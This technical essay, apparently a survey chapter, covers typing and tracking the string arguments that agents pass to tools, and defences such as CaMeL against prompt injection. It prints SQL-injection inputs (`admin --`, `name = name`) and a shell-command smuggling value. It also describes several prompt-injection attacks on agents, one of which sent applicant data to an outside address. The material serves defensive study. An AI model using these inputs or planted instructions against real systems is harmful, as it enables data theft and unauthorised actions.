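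*Methods for Formal Verification of Agent Skills* (2026) names Liquid Haskell, F\* and Dafny as tools that already support refinement types. *λ_A* (2026), a formal language for describing agents, also includes refinement types. It gives all of a model's inputs and outputs the basic type Str, so any narrower type has to come from a refinement or another construction built on Str.

Knowles lets the condition in a refinement type be any program that returns true or false. No algorithm can decide every comparison between such conditions, so he uses what he calls hybrid type checking. The checker accepts the code if it proves that one type is a subtype of the other, rejects the code if it disproves this, and otherwise inserts a test that runs with the program. He proved that any decidable substitute for his type system either misses some error that the hybrid method catches before the program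 runs or rejects some correct program that the hybrid method accepts.

### The model writes after the compiler has finished

A compiler runs before the model writes any argument, so it cannot guarantee that `number` will consist of digits. The tool has to check the argument on every call. With static types, the compiler can reject a handler that could pass the raw argument to the database without this check, or that later changes the checked value into something the type does not cover.

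*Methods for Formal Verification of Agent Skills* applies refinement types to skills, which are packages of instructions and scripts that an agent can load. Analysing the scripts in advance doesn't reveal which calls the model will make, so the paper proposes a refinement type for the dispatcher, the code that forwards calls to the host's functions. The type excludes any capability missing from the skill's declared list. Because the model chooses the capability at run time, the dispatcher still has to check the list when the call arrives, but the type prevents a programmer from leaving out the check.

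*Refinement types in Jolie* (Tchitchigin, Safina and colleagues, 2016) proposes the same division for Jolie, a language for building systems from small services that exchange messages. Its string types are defined by regular expressions and can describe, for example, GUIDs, which are identifiers made of hexadecimal digits in a fixed layout. Calls from outside, which may be malicious, are checked at run time. For calls between Jolie services, Z3, an automated solver from Microsoft Research, checks the types in advance. In a tool server, the model counts as an outside caller and the handlers as internal services.

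Tchitchigin and colleagues use the example of a news board that finds a user by name and then fetches the user's posts by identifier. A faulty version of the code passes the name instead of the identifier, and an ordinary string type accepts both. With a refinement type for GUIDs, Z3 proved the correct version well typed. On the faulty version its search never ended, which they attribute to simplifications in their encoding. A developer who relies on such a solver needs to set a time limit and treat a timeout as a rejection.

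### Credentials that exclude "admin --"

Knowles built his ideas into a language called SAGE, and one of his examples concerns SQL injection. A login function pastes a user name and a password into this query and admits the user if the count is above zero:

```sql
SELECT count(*) FROM client WHERE name =... and pwd=...
```

If somebody enters the user name `admin --` and an empty password, the two hyphens turn the password condition into a comment. Knowles therefore defines a type `Credential` of strings made up only of letters and digits, and the login function accepts two credentials instead of two strings.

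The program around it reads both values from the keyboard and passes them on unchecked, which is a type error. SAGE cannot prove this, because it would have to show that the programmer's own matching function rejects at least one string. So it accepts the program and inserts a test before the call. When somebody enters `admin --`, the test fails and the program stops before it builds the query. SAGE also stores the string in a database as a counterexample to the claim that every string is a credential. The next time it compiles this code, it finds the counterexample and rejects the call, so the programmer has to decide how to handle a bad name. A tool would usually return an error message so that the model can try again.

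The type does not protect the query as printed, because the query has no quotation marks around the values and SQL reads an unquoted word as a column name. The type accepts `name` and `pwd` as credentials, but they turn the condition into `name = name and pwd = pwd`. This is true for every row where neither column is null, so the login succeeds without a password. Under Ray and Ligatti's definition, this is an injection, since the database has to look the names up. With quotation marks around both values, the type does protect the query, because no string of letters and digits can close a quotation. However, the type also excludes names like O'Brien and any password with punctuation.

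### The sql-safe? predicate

Typed Scheme adds a type checker to Scheme. After a test for whether `x` is a number, the checker treats `x` as a number in the branch where the test succeeded. *The Design and Implementation of Typed Scheme* (Tobin-Hochstadt and Felleisen, 2011) extends this to tests that programmers write themselves. The paper's example is `sql-safe?`, a function that decides whether a string is acceptable in a query. One declaration turns `sql-safe?` into a refinement type, and the function that queries the database accepts only strings of that type.

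The type checker never examines what `sql-safe?` does. It uses only the fact that the test returned true for a particular value, so it needs no solver or proof search. For the same reason, it cannot infer that one test implies another, so a number that has passed a test for at most eight digits must still pass a separate test for at most twelve. Tobin-Hochstadt and Felleisen point out that programmers have to trust only the predicate, which the database's vendor could supply.

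They also give a function that prepares an ordinary string for the query. In Python, their function would look like this:

```python
def sanitize(s):
    escaped = escape(s)
    if sql_safe(s):
        return s
    raise ValueError("escape failed")
```

The function computes an escaped copy, then tests and returns the original. If the predicate rejects a lone apostrophe, `O'Brien` causes an error even though the escaping worked. The type checker correctly accepts this code because every string the function returns has passed the test. A function that returned `Acme` for every customer would also have the correct type.

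### Structure in place of a string

A pattern check works out the structure of a string and then discards that structure, so later code has to parse the string again. Kelly and colleagues propose keeping the structure. Their SafeString has four parts: a grammar, a recognizer that turns a string into a parse tree or fails, a conversion of the tree into ordinary data, and a function that turns the data back into text. A web page's colour code, for example, becomes three numbers. `#F65T00` fails because T is not a hexadecimal digit, while `#000` and `#000000` both become the same three numbers, for black.

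Kelly and colleagues represent a file path as a list of folders with a file name and extension. The developer of `read_file` can go further if the reports are monthly and have predictable names:

```python
def read_report(year: int, month: int):
    require(2000 <= year <= 2099 and 1 <= month <= 12)
    return open_in(user_folder(), f"{year}-{month:02d}.pdf")
```

`user_folder()` takes the user from the login session, and `open_in` stands for a directory-confined open, as in `os.Root` or `openat2`. The schema now declares two whole numbers, so the JSON parser does all the parsing. The model can name 1,200 files in one folder but can't write `..`, a slash or the name of a link, so the confinement only has to handle links that somebody else put there.

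Some arguments, such as a customer's name, have no structure to extract, but the developer can confine the name to one tool. That tool binds the name as a parameter in a customer search and returns customer numbers, which the other tools accept. For strings that do have structure, somebody has to write the grammar, the recognizer and the conversion back. Kelly and colleagues suggest that libraries supply these for common kinds of string. They evaluate their method with three case studies in TypeScript, on e-mail addresses, file paths and strings in web pages, which illustrate the method but don't measure how many errors it prevents.

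### A misplaced hyphen, and how a solver finds it

A pattern can be wrong in ways that its author doesn't see. Amadini (2020), in *A Survey on String Constraint Solving*, discusses a line from MyEasyMarket, a web application, that deletes every character outside a permitted set from a visitor's input. The pattern for the characters to delete is

```
[^A-Za-z0-9 .-@:\/]
```

The author wanted to keep letters, digits, spaces and the symbols `.`, `-`, `@`, `:` and `/`. But inside square brackets, a hyphen between two characters means a range, and in ASCII the range from `.` to `@` also includes `;`, `<`, `=`, `>` and `?`. The application therefore keeps `<`, which can begin a script in the page it sends to a browser, and deletes hyphens. A backslash before the hyphen fixes both problems.

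A string solver can find such mistakes. It takes conditions on unknown strings and either finds strings that meet them all or, when it can, proves that none exist. Amadini suggests modelling the replacement and adding the condition that the result contains `<`. In the standard input language for such solvers, a simplified version is:

```
(declare-const s String)
(assert (str.in_re s (re.* (re.union
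    (re.range "A" "Z") (re.range "a" "z") (re.range "0" "9")
    (re.range "." "@") (str.to_re " ")))))
(assert (str.contains s "<"))
(check-sat)
```

The solver reports that the conditions are satisfiable, for instance by the string `<`. With the corrected pattern it reports that they are unsatisfiable, a result that covers every possible string, as no amount of testing could. But the developer still had to think of checking for `<`. It is safer to list the permitted characters individually and ask the solver for a string that the list and the pattern treat differently. This check would also reveal the missing hyphen.

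### Which questions about strings have an algorithm

The test at a tool's boundary only has to check one string against a pattern, which is easy. A static type checker has the harder task of deciding whether every string of one type also belongs to another. If regular expressions define both types, an algorithm can always decide this. It converts each expression into an automaton, a machine with finitely many states that reads a string one character at a time and ends by accepting or rejecting it. It then swaps accept and reject in the second automaton, runs both together, and searches for a string that both accept. Such a string belongs to the first type but not the second. The search always ends because there are only finitely many pairs of states.

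Kelly and colleagues note that this problem is PSPACE-complete, so no known method is fast on all inputs, though patterns in tool schemas are usually short. The result applies to regular expressions in the strict sense, which exclude features such as backreferences because these can describe languages that no finite automaton can recognize.

SQL and most programming languages need a context-free grammar because they allow nesting to any depth, such as bracketed conditions inside other conditions. No algorithm can decide, for every pair of context-free grammars, whether the second generates every string that the first does. A developer who writes a small grammar for permitted queries therefore can't count on a program to confirm that the database's grammar accepts them all. But an algorithm can always decide whether a context-free language is contained in a regular one, so the developer can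 prove that no query in the small grammar contains a semicolon or names a table outside a short list.

Conditions that combine several operations on strings are harder still:

| Conditions on the unknown strings | Is there an algorithm for every case? |
|---|---|
| equations between joined strings | yes (Makanin, 1977) |
| regular expressions, lengths and joining | yes |
| equations between joined strings, with lengths | unknown |
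| regular expressions, lengths, joining and conversion between text and numbers | no |
| equations in which one string results from replacing all occurrences of a piece of text in another | no, unless the equations have a restricted form |

The last row applies to escaping, because doubling every apostrophe is a replacement of this kind. Amadini describes a restricted form, called straight-line, that keeps the question decidable. In this form, each string may depend only on strings computed earlier, as is usually the case in a handler without loops.

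Practical questions rarely fall into a class that has been proven undecidable. *String Theories involving Regular Membership Predicates* (Berzish, Day and colleagues, 2021) sorted 56,993 test problems from industrial uses and solver developers. About 51% belonged to a class that this paper or other work had shown decidable, and none used the combination that the paper proved undecidable. The largest group with equations has 22,604 problems, which also involve lengths and regular expressions. Nobody knows whether an algorithm can settle every problem of that type. The test problems come from program analysis, and checking one tool argument is usually simpler.

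### Grammars that constrain the model's own text

Strict modes leave free text almost unrestricted, but a developer can restrict that too. OpenAI's custom tools can include a regular expression or a context-free grammar in the notation of Lark, a parsing library. Programs for running open models, such as llama.cpp and vLLM, offer similar options. A grammar for a narrow version of `run_query` might be:

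```
start:  "SELECT " column (", " column)* " FROM my_invoices WHERE customer = " TEXT
column: "number" | "amount" | "due_date"
TEXT:   /'([^']|'')*'/
```

At each step, the model assigns a probability to every next token. The software removes the tokens that could not lead to a complete text in the grammar, scales up the remaining probabilities to add up to one, and picks from those. With this grammar, the model can't write a deletion, a second statement or the name of another table, regardless of any planted instructions. The pattern for `TEXT` follows SQL's rule of doubling apostrophes, so the only way to write Ms O'Brien's name is `'O''Brien'`.

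Removing forbidden tokens during generation can turn an error into a wrong answer. If the model has written `'O'` and was about to write `Brien`, the grammar forbids the B. The model can escape the apostrophe by adding a second one, but if it ends the string there, the query is valid and looks for a customer called O. Enumerations have the same effect. Suppose a user asks for overdue invoices, but the only permitted statuses are draft, sent and paid. The model gives "overdue" a probability of 90%, "sent" 5%, "paid" 4% and "draft" 1%. Removing "overdue" raises the other three to 50%, 40% and 10%, so half the time the user receives sent invoices. A validator would have rejected "overdue" and returned an error that the model could explain to the user. An enumeration should therefore include a value such as "none of these" if a request might not fit.

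Whoever runs the model provides the guarantee, which covers only finished texts because a length limit may cut one off. A tool server usually can't tell whether the caller's model was constrained by the grammar, so it should parse the argument again before using it. The grammar must also match the database's syntax, for instance on whether a backslash escapes an apostrophe. A provider may support only simple grammars, and OpenAI's guide says its service can reject one that is too complex.

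### Safe for which interpreter?

The main objection to types such as `sql-safe?` is that a string is safe only for a particular interpreter. Escaping `O'Brien` for SQL gives `O''Brien`. If the handler puts that on an invoice, the customer sees two apostrophes. A shell that reads it as part of a command drops both and passes on `OBrien`. A check that considers only quoted SQL also accepts `march.docx; echo hello`, which is dangerous in a shell command. Even "safe for SQL" is too broad, since a credential that is data inside quotation marks can act as a column name without them.

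This objection is weak against very narrow types. Eight digits on their own are plain data as an SQL value, a shell argument, a file name or a search pattern, and a developer can check each use in a few minutes. The objection is strong against any type that has to allow names. For such values, it is better to define the type by what the value means and convert the value only at the point of use. For example, `CustomerName` holds `O'Brien` exactly as the customer writes it. The database receives the name as a parameter, and a program receives it in an argument list. A function that escapes the name for a web page returns a separate type, `HtmlText`, which the query function doesn't accept.

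Tobin-Hochstadt and Felleisen prefer a refinement to a wrapper because any function that takes a string also takes a checked string, with no unwrapping. For an escaped string this is a drawback, because the type checker allows `O''Brien` anywhere it allows a string. A wrapper makes the programmer unwrap the text explicitly, so a reviewer can see where it leaves its intended context.

Types help less when a value is well formed but wrong. Kelly and colleagues mention that a correct e-mail address may belong to nobody. Knowles's conditions can be any program, so a developer could define a type of invoice numbers that belong to the logged-in user's own customers. The tool would have to look up ownership on every call, and the answer could change before the value is used, much as a folder can change between checking a file and opening it. Putting the ownership condition in the query itself avoids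 that gap.

Even this type still allows mistakes. Suppose an employee who manages both Acme and its competitor asks for Acme's invoices while the model is reading an e-mail that tells it to fetch the competitor's. Both customer numbers have the right type, and the employee is allowed to see both sets of invoices. No condition on the number alone can distinguish the wrong call from a correct one, because the competitor's number would be correct if the employee had asked for it.

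## Does it help to track where a string came from?

With a record of who supplied each value, a checker could distinguish a customer number the employee asked for from the same number planted in an e-mail. Taint tracking keeps such a record by marking data from untrusted sources and following it to wherever the program uses it.

### Taint mode in Perl

Perl, which programmers often used for CGI scripts, had taint checks for some programs by 1989, and version 5 added a switch for them in 1994. With the switch on, Perl marks data as tainted if it comes from a source outside the program, such as command-line arguments, environment variables or files. If an expression contains one tainted value, Perl may treat the whole result as tainted. Perl stops the program when a tainted value reaches a sink, which is an operation that can do harm, such as starting a shell or changing a file.

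A Perl version of `convert_report` might begin like this:

```perl
my $filename = shift;            # a command-line argument, so marked
if ($filename =~ /^(\w[\w.-]*)$/) {
    $filename = $1;              # the captured text has no mark
} else {
    die "unacceptable file name";
}
```

Without the test, Perl would refuse to pass `$filename` to a command. The programmer clears the mark by matching the value against a pattern and keeping the part that the brackets capture. Perl doesn't check how strict the pattern is, so `/(.+)/`, which accepts nearly any text, clears the mark too. Tracking therefore makes the check hard to forget, but the check is an ordinary allowlist and can be wrong.

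Perl's taint mode also has gaps, and the Perl manual describes it as "intended to prevent stupid mistakes, not to remove the need for thought". It lets a program read a file whose name is marked, so it would not stop a path traversal in `read_file`. A program may also use a marked value to choose between two strings that the programmer wrote, and the chosen string is not marked.

Ruby copied the mechanism and later dropped it. Naruse wrote in *Remove $SAFE, taint and trust* that nobody used it any more and that libraries that handled input usually didn't set the mark. Ruby 2.7 made the marking functions do nothing (Saeloun, *Ruby 2.7 removes taint checking mechanism*, 2020). An agent likewise depends on its tools to set the mark. If `fetch_page` returns a page without one, every later check treats the page as trusted.

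### What a model does to the marks

Perl can track which values went into the result of an expression. But in a language model, any part of the context (all the text it has received so far) may affect any word it writes, so a strict marking rule gives every argument the marks of everything in the context.

FIDES, a system described in *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control* (2025), gives each piece of data two labels, trusted or untrusted and public or secret. When it combines data, it keeps the more cautious label of each pair. A short conversation with the invoicing assistant shows what happens if one model reads everything:

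| New text in the context | Its labels | Labels of the whole context |
|---|---|---|
| the user asks for the March report as a PDF | trusted, public | trusted, public |
| `find_invoices` returns Acme's invoices | trusted, secret | trusted, secret |
| `fetch_page` returns a supplier's page | untrusted, public | untrusted, secret |
| the user asks for the April report as a PDF | trusted, public | untrusted, secret |

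FIDES checks each tool call against the labels of the context and the arguments, according to *SPA* (2026). If `convert_report` requires a file name from a trusted source, FIDES now refuses the call for the April report, even though the user typed the name. *Optimizing Agent Planning for Security and Autonomy* (2026) notes that the context label "can quickly become too restrictive".

A looser rule could mark an argument as untrusted only if its text also appears in an untrusted source. It would miss any value that the model had reworded. It would also miss cases where the model copies nothing, such as when a supplier's e-mail leads it to call `run_command`, a tool name that comes from the developer's own list.

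The usual solution is to keep untrusted text away from the model that makes decisions. Willison proposed the dual-model pattern for this in 2023. A privileged model reads the user's request and chooses the tool calls. A quarantined model reads e-mails and web pages but has no tools. Its output goes into variables that the privileged model can pass along by name without reading their contents. This works for summarizing an e-mail, but not for tasks in which the next step depends on what the e-mail contains.

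### Passing on numbers and choices

*Preventing Prompt Injection with Type-Directed Privilege Separation* (Jacob, Alghamdi and colleagues, 2025) describes a design in which the quarantined model may give the privileged model integers, floating-point numbers, true-or-false values and choices from a list that the developer wrote, but no free text. Even if an attacker fully controls the quarantined model, it can pass on only a wrong number or a wrong choice, neither of which can contain an instruction. Arrays have to be short, because a long one could spell out a message number by number. It seems wise to limit the size of each integer for the same reason.

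Jacob and colleagues built three agents, each with and without this protection:

- **A shopping agent** looks for a product in a simulated shop, where anybody can write a review. The quarantined model gives each review two scores from 0 to 10, for how strongly it supports the product and how relevant it is. The privileged model receives the median scores and the number of reviews. In the attack, a review contained a false safety alert telling the agent to leave the page.
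- **A calendar agent** arranges a meeting by e-mail. The quarantined model reduces the other person's replies to a list of one-hour slots. In the attack, the other person asked for the user's calendar.
- **A bug-fixing agent** reads a public bug report. The quarantined model returns a category, the size of the likely fix, and the places to look, as file numbers and line numbers. Another model writes three plans from these, and a quarantined judge returns the number of the best. In the attack, the report asked for an extra file.

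| Agent | Tasks completed, unprotected | Tasks completed, protected | Attacks that succeeded, unprotected | Attacks that succeeded, protected |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| shopping (GPT-4o) | 21.8% | 22.4% | 31.7% | 0% |
| calendar (GPT-4o) | 90.0% | 91.0% | 63.0% | 0% |
| bug fixing (GPT-5.2) | 68.3% | 45.0% | 98.9% | 0% |

The tests used only one attack text per agent, so the zeros are weaker evidence of security than the design itself. The task completion figures are more informative. The two simpler agents lost none of their successes, but the bug-fixing agent lost about a third, which Jacob and colleagues attribute to the plain-language explanations in real bug reports. They also needed considerable testing to find a suitable set of fields.

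A fixed list cannot represent values its developer didn't foresee. The calendar's slots ran from 8 a.m. to 5 p.m., so someone who could meet only at 7 p.m. could not choose that time. The developer can add a "none of these" option, but then a person has to read the message.

The types also don't prevent deception, since enough fake reviews would raise the median score. The calendar agent may have another weakness. It copies a description of the meeting, possibly taken from the other person's e-mails, into the user's calendar without reading it. The privileged model reads that calendar when it arranges the next meeting, so an instruction planted in the description could reach it then, as in a second-order SQL injection. The tests each covered only one meeting, so they would not have revealed this.

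### CaMeL: a program written before the data arrives

CaMeL (Debenedetti and colleagues, Google DeepMind, 2025) develops the dual-model pattern further, and *CaMeLoT* (Nikolaou, Eckhoff and colleagues, 2026) describes and extends CaMeL. The privileged model writes a complete program in a restricted form of Python, based on the user's request. An interpreter runs the program and makes the tool calls. The program calls the quarantined model like a function, for example to find an e-mail address in a block of text.

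The program is written before any untrusted text arrives, so a planted instruction cannot add a tool call to it, just as a customer's name cannot alter a parameterized query. But an outsider can still change a value the program uses. If the program looks for Bob's address in a chat channel and sends him a message, anyone who can write in the channel may be able to supply a different address.

CaMeL therefore attaches to every value a record of its sources and of who may read it. Before each tool call, the interpreter runs a policy, a Python function that receives the arguments with their records and either allows or denies the call. In Nikolaou and colleagues' extension, a value computed from several others takes the least trusted of their origins, in this order:

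program's own text < user < untrusted tool output < quarantined model

Untrusted data can still determine which of the program's existing branches runs, as a marked value can in Perl. This is harmless when the choice is between sort orders. If the program pays an invoice whenever the quarantined model's output is that the bank details match, the supplier's text may determine whether money leaves the account. A policy on the payment tool can check where the account number came from, but the decision to pay may still depend on the supplier's text.

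### One address from two sources

Suppose the user types an address and asks for a summary of the page. The privileged model writes one call:

```python
terms = fetch_page("https://acme.example/terms")
```

If the user instead asks for the terms that Acme's home page links to, the program has to find the address:

```python
home  = fetch_page("https://acme.example/")
link  = ask_quarantined("Find the address of the terms page", home)
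terms = fetch_page(link)
```

Suppose `link` turns out to be `https://acme.example/terms`, the same 26 characters. Any check on the text would treat the two calls alike. A policy in the style of CaMeL can treat them differently:

```python
TRUSTED = {"program", "user", "invoices"}

def fetch_page_policy(url):
    if not url.sources <= TRUSTED:
        return Deny("this address came from outside the firm")
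    if host_of(url) not in url.readers:
        return Deny("this address contains private data")
    return Allow()
```

The user is the source of the typed address and anyone may read it, so the policy allows the call. The copied address comes from the home page and the quarantined model, so the policy denies the call. Whoever controls the page chose that address and could have chosen one that confirms an order. The second condition covers cases such as the program adding Ms O'Brien's balance to an address that the user typed. All the sources are then trusted, but only the firm's staff may read the balance.

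Nikolaou and colleagues' checker could refuse the copied address earlier, before any tool runs. It converts the privileged model's program into a diagram of possible steps and searches for a path that breaks a rule. If it finds one, it returns the path to the model, which can write a better program. Because the checker simplifies loops, it may also reject some safe programs.

Jacob and colleagues' types would not make this case safe. Even if the quarantined model returned the number of a link on the page, and the privileged model read no text from the page, the page's author would still have chosen the address that number refers to. The bug-fixing agent could use file numbers safely because its list of files came from the code repository.

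The policy also has a drawback, because the user wanted the terms and the link was probably fine. The assistant can show the user the address and ask before opening it. The developer could also accept a link from a page if it stays on the host the user named, which would allow Acme's terms and refuse an address at `collector.example`.

### What CaMeL stops and what it costs

Most tests of CaMeL use AgentDojo, a benchmark with 97 ordinary tasks in simulated workplace, banking, travel and chat accounts. Attackers plant instructions in the data that the agent reads. In *SecureClaw* (2026), none of 629 attacks succeeded against CaMeL, but CaMeL completed only 29 of the 97 ordinary tasks. SecureClaw itself, a rival system, completed 59, but its developers ran the comparison and had to adapt CaMeL's code to do so.

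*The Devil is in the Context* (2026) reports a similar trade-off on newly written cases. CaMeL reduced successful attacks from 17.5% to 2.5% but completed 27.5% of tasks. Another defence, PromptArmor, allowed 7.5% of attacks and completed 90% of tasks. The percentages suggest 40 cases for each system, so CaMeL may have allowed one attack and PromptArmor three.

CaMeL's advantage is clearer when attackers plant false data instead of instructions. *Agent Data Injection Attacks are Realistic Threats to AI Agents* (2026) found that planted instructions hardly ever worked, even on an unprotected agent, but false data got past every defence tested except CaMeL with strict policies. A false address contains no instruction that a model could learn to ignore, so a record of its source is more useful.

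CaMeL may lower the completion rate less with better models. Peters-Gill, Semler and colleagues (2026), in *Can CaMeLs Talk?*, tested it on 112 tasks from another benchmark, AssetOpsBench. It lowered the completion rate by 21.6 percentage points on average over five models, and by 13.4 points for the two strongest, Claude Fable 5 and GPT-5.5. One difficulty is that the privileged model has to write code to unpack a tool's output before it has received any. Peters-Gill and colleagues had to add a description of the output to every tool before CaMeL worked reasonably well.

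### When one agent instructs another

Sometimes the program that reads a string argument is another agent. Peters-Gill and colleagues built a system in which one agent queried a database of job applicants, a second coordinated the work, and a third sent messages. All three used CaMeL. The coordinating agent pasted a summary of the data into its request:

```python
notification_agent(f"Send this summary to Julie via Slack: {summary}")
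```

An instruction planted in the database became part of that string. The notification agent treated the whole string as its user's request and also e-mailed the applicants' details to an outside address. The coordinating agent had marked the summary as untrusted, but the notification agent didn't receive the mark. The handler for `find_invoices` had a similar flaw because it pasted a customer's name into SQL.

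The remedy resembles a parameterized query. The call takes a message, which the receiving agent treats as an instruction, and a set of variables, which its privileged model cannot read. The interpreter rejects any message that depends on a tool's output, and the variables keep their marks. Across five models with 949 attacks each, the average attack success rate was 12.9% without CaMeL, 0.2% with CaMeL in each agent, and 0.0% with the new protocol. All the attacks that succeeded against the separate CaMeL agents exploited this gap.

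Two models account for most of the 12.9%. Attacks succeeded 36.1% of the time against GPT-4.1 and 24.6% against Gemini 2.5 Pro, while none succeeded against GPT-5.5, even without protection. Peters-Gill and colleagues switched off CaMeL's policies, so their results measure only the effect of the separation. Stopping an attack that changes a value within a valid plan would require a policy.

### A rule for each argument

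Santos-Grueiro (2026), in *Context-to-Execution Integrity for LLM Agents*, a single-author preprint, sets the rules for each argument separately. His system, CXI, lets a model read untrusted text and propose a call, and a gate then checks the call before the tool runs. If *W* is text that an outsider can write and *X* is a protected argument, the rule is

*W* ↛ *X* unless *W* → *D* → *X*

where *D* is a typed release, a value that trusted code has checked and approved for that one argument. A build log may therefore supply the path of the file that failed, but it can't choose the tool or mark the change as approved. To avoid the blending problem, CXI can write each protected argument in a separate model call whose prompt contains only trusted text and valid releases.

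For the invoicing assistant, a developer might decide as follows:

| Argument | If the value comes from a supplier's e-mail |
|---|---|
| invoice number | accept it if the invoice belongs to that supplier |
| customer number | refuse it unless the user also named the customer |
| name of a report to convert | refuse it |
| text of a note | store it as data and keep the mark |

This would stop an e-mail from leading the assistant to a competitor's invoices, even if the employee has permission to read them. CXI also checks whether a call may happen at all, because planted text could make an agent repeat a permitted call.

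In 192 test cases, a check of the schema alone let every unauthorized call through. CXI blocked them all and accepted every legitimate call. Santos-Grueiro wrote both the cases and the policies, so these results mainly show that CXI works as he designed it. In 400 live coding tasks, CXI let no unauthorized call through, and the agent completed 231 tasks safely. Of the rest, 73 failed because the output was unreadable and 61 because the change lacked authorization. The other 35 failed because an authorized change didn't solve the problem, and he notes that a call can have valid authority and still be wrong.

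Writing the policies takes work. The policies for 24 kinds of operation covered 149 arguments, of which 85 needed protection. An audit found 18 problems, nine of them severe. The gate enforces the policy only as written, so a developer who wrongly classifies an argument leaves it unprotected.

### Marks on the rows of a database

An agent's data often passes through a database, where a query can combine marked and unmarked rows. Summers, Mohammed and Wu (2025), in *Please Don't Kill My Vibe*, argue that databases should enforce data-flow policies themselves, as they already enforce permissions. With FlowGuard, their early version of this, a developer could protect the firm's notes like this:

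```
POLICY OVER notes
CONSTRAINT bool_and(sanitized)
ON FAIL KILL ROW
```

The column `sanitized` is false for anything a user or agent writes, until a check sets it to true. The policy keeps a result row only if every note that contributed to it has passed the check. If one of Acme's forty notes hasn't passed, a query that counts notes per customer returns no row for Acme. A similar policy can remove totals based on fewer than three people, which would limit attacks that combine permitted queries to work out a private figure.

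FlowGuard enforces these policies by rewriting the query. In early tests with one simple policy, most queries took almost no extra time. Methods that first record where every result came from added at least ten times as much.

The rule about notes is stricter than necessary, because a count contains no text that could carry an instruction. For columns of free text, the harder problem is deciding when to set `sanitized` to true. Summers and colleagues suggest having a user check the row or testing it with a regular expression. A regular expression can confirm that a value is an invoice number, but it can't reliably recognize every instruction to a language model. FlowGuard also doesn't yet follow data through other tools, so the marks don't extend beyond the database.

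### Harmful strings from trusted people

A trustworthy source can still supply a bad string. If a user copies a link from a fraudulent e-mail into the chat, the assistant records the user as the link's source, because tracking begins only when the text enters the program. The policy for `fetch_page` then allows the link. The tool should therefore refuse private network addresses, no matter who typed the URL.

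The firm's own database raises a similar problem. The table of labels above treats Acme's invoices as trusted because they came from `find_invoices`, but a supplier or customer may have written some of their text. Labeling each column by who can write to it is safer than trusting everything the tool returns, but it can bring back the original difficulty because much of a firm's data may contain text from outsiders.

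Tracking a string's origin also doesn't show how an interpreter will parse it, so the handler has to bind a customer's name as a parameter even when the user typed the name.

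## When should a tool accept a whole program as a string?

Binding a value or tracking its source does little to protect `run_query` and `run_command`, because their arguments are whole programs. The developer can replace these tools with narrower ones, or keep them and limit what the programs can access.

### The case for narrow tools

If the developer replaces both tools with `find_invoices`, `send_reminder(invoice_number)` and `mark_paid(invoice_number)`, they can read and test every action the assistant can take, and decide which ones need a person's approval. Text planted in a supplier's e-mail may still lead the model to mark the wrong invoice as paid, but it cannot make the assistant delete a table, because no tool does that. Rice's theorem implies that no checker can always give the same assurance about arbitrary commands.

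*Design Patterns for Securing LLM Agents against Prompt Injections* calls the strictest version of this the action-selector pattern. The model turns a request into one of several actions that the developer has defined, perhaps filling in a few values, and never reads what the action returns. According to the paper, general-purpose agents are unlikely to offer reliable safety guarantees while they and their defences rely on the current kind of language model. It recommends agents built for one application, and suggests replacing general commands with specific ones, such as a plain search tool in place of `find`.

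Anthropic's *Agent Harness Design* (2026) notes that a bash tool gives the harness, the software that carries out a model's tool calls, "only a command string", which has the same form for every action. A dedicated tool gives the harness typed arguments that it can block, log or show to the user. Anthropic recommends dedicated tools for actions that need a security boundary, especially those that are hard to undo. A dedicated tool can also include checks suited to its action. For example, an editing tool can refuse to overwrite a file that has changed since the model last read it, whereas a harness with only a bash tool would first have to work out which file the command will overwrite.

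Narrow tools also leave better records. *MCP vs CLI for AI Agents* (2026) compares a structured log of who did what with shell command history, which it rates as unreliable.

Task-specific tools can also improve an agent's results. *TheMCPCompany* (2025) compared agents that had task-specific tools with agents that had a web browser, using tasks from TheAgentCompany, a benchmark that simulates a software firm. The agents with task-specific tools did better at lower cost, even when they had to search for the right tools themselves. However, the agents that had to search scored 8.4 points lower on average than agents given exactly the tools each task required.

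### The case for open-ended languages

Narrow tools cover only the requests somebody foresaw. If a user asks whether customers pay more slowly in summer, a short SQL query may answer that, but none of the three narrow tools will. Elastic, which sells a search engine, advises developers to include a general tool that lets the agent write full queries, so that it isn't limited to the questions the specialized tools can answer.

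Large sets of tools also slow a model down, because it has to process every tool's description and every result. In November 2025, Anthropic suggested letting the model write code that loads and calls only the tools it needs. In Anthropic's example, this cut the text the model had to process from 150,000 tokens to 2,000. The code can also filter a 10,000-row spreadsheet and return only five rows. GitHub cut the number of default tools for its Copilot assistant in one code editor from 40 to 13 and reported higher success rates on two programming benchmarks. This supports using fewer tools, but it doesn't show whether the remaining ones should be narrow or general.

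Models are also good at using shells. According to Anthropic, Claude 3.5 Sonnet solved 49% of SWE-bench Verified, a set of real programming problems, using only a bash tool and a text editor. This was the best result at the time. Xu, Zhang and Arunachalam (2026) explain in *From model to agent* that OpenAI offers a shell because its earlier code tool ran only Python, while a shell can also run programs in other languages, start a server or send requests to other services.

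On this view, the place to set limits is the effect, with a sandbox for commands and a restricted database account for queries.

### Experiments with shells and typed tools

In *Is Bash All You Need?*, Mak, Suresh and colleagues (2026) tested this disagreement on office work. They gave Claude Opus 4.8 and GPT-5.5 the same tasks with typed tools, a shell, both, or programmatic tool calling, in which the model writes a program that can act only by calling the typed tools. One benchmark, TheAgentCompany, supplied 174 tasks involving chat, shared files, programming and project planning. Another, APEX-Agents, supplied 480 tasks in banking, consulting and corporate law.

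| Average score | TheAgentCompany, Opus 4.8 | TheAgentCompany, GPT-5.5 | APEX-Agents, Opus 4.8 | APEX-Agents, GPT-5.5 |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| typed tools | 44.9% | 45.3% | 41.1% | 39.8% |
| programs over typed tools | 52.9% | 45.1% | 40.1% | 37.8% |
| shell and typed tools | 67.2% | 66.3% | 47.2% | 45.5% |
| shell only | 69.4% | 67.1% | 48.5% | 44.6% |

These scores include partial credit. On TheAgentCompany, Opus 4.8 fully solved 50.6% of the tasks with a shell and 24.1% with typed tools. Agents with only a shell processed 19% to 72% fewer tokens than agents with typed tools. In a fifth version, agents could write their own tools and save them for later tasks, but this made no detectable difference to the score.

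Programmatic tool calling lets a model write programs that loop over typed tools and combine their results, yet it scored about the same as single calls in three of the four columns. This suggests that the shell helped mainly by letting the agent do things that no typed tool covered. The shell may also have had an advantage because models have less practice at writing programs over typed tools. On TheAgentCompany, 65.2% of programmatic calls succeeded, compared with 92.1% of shell calls.

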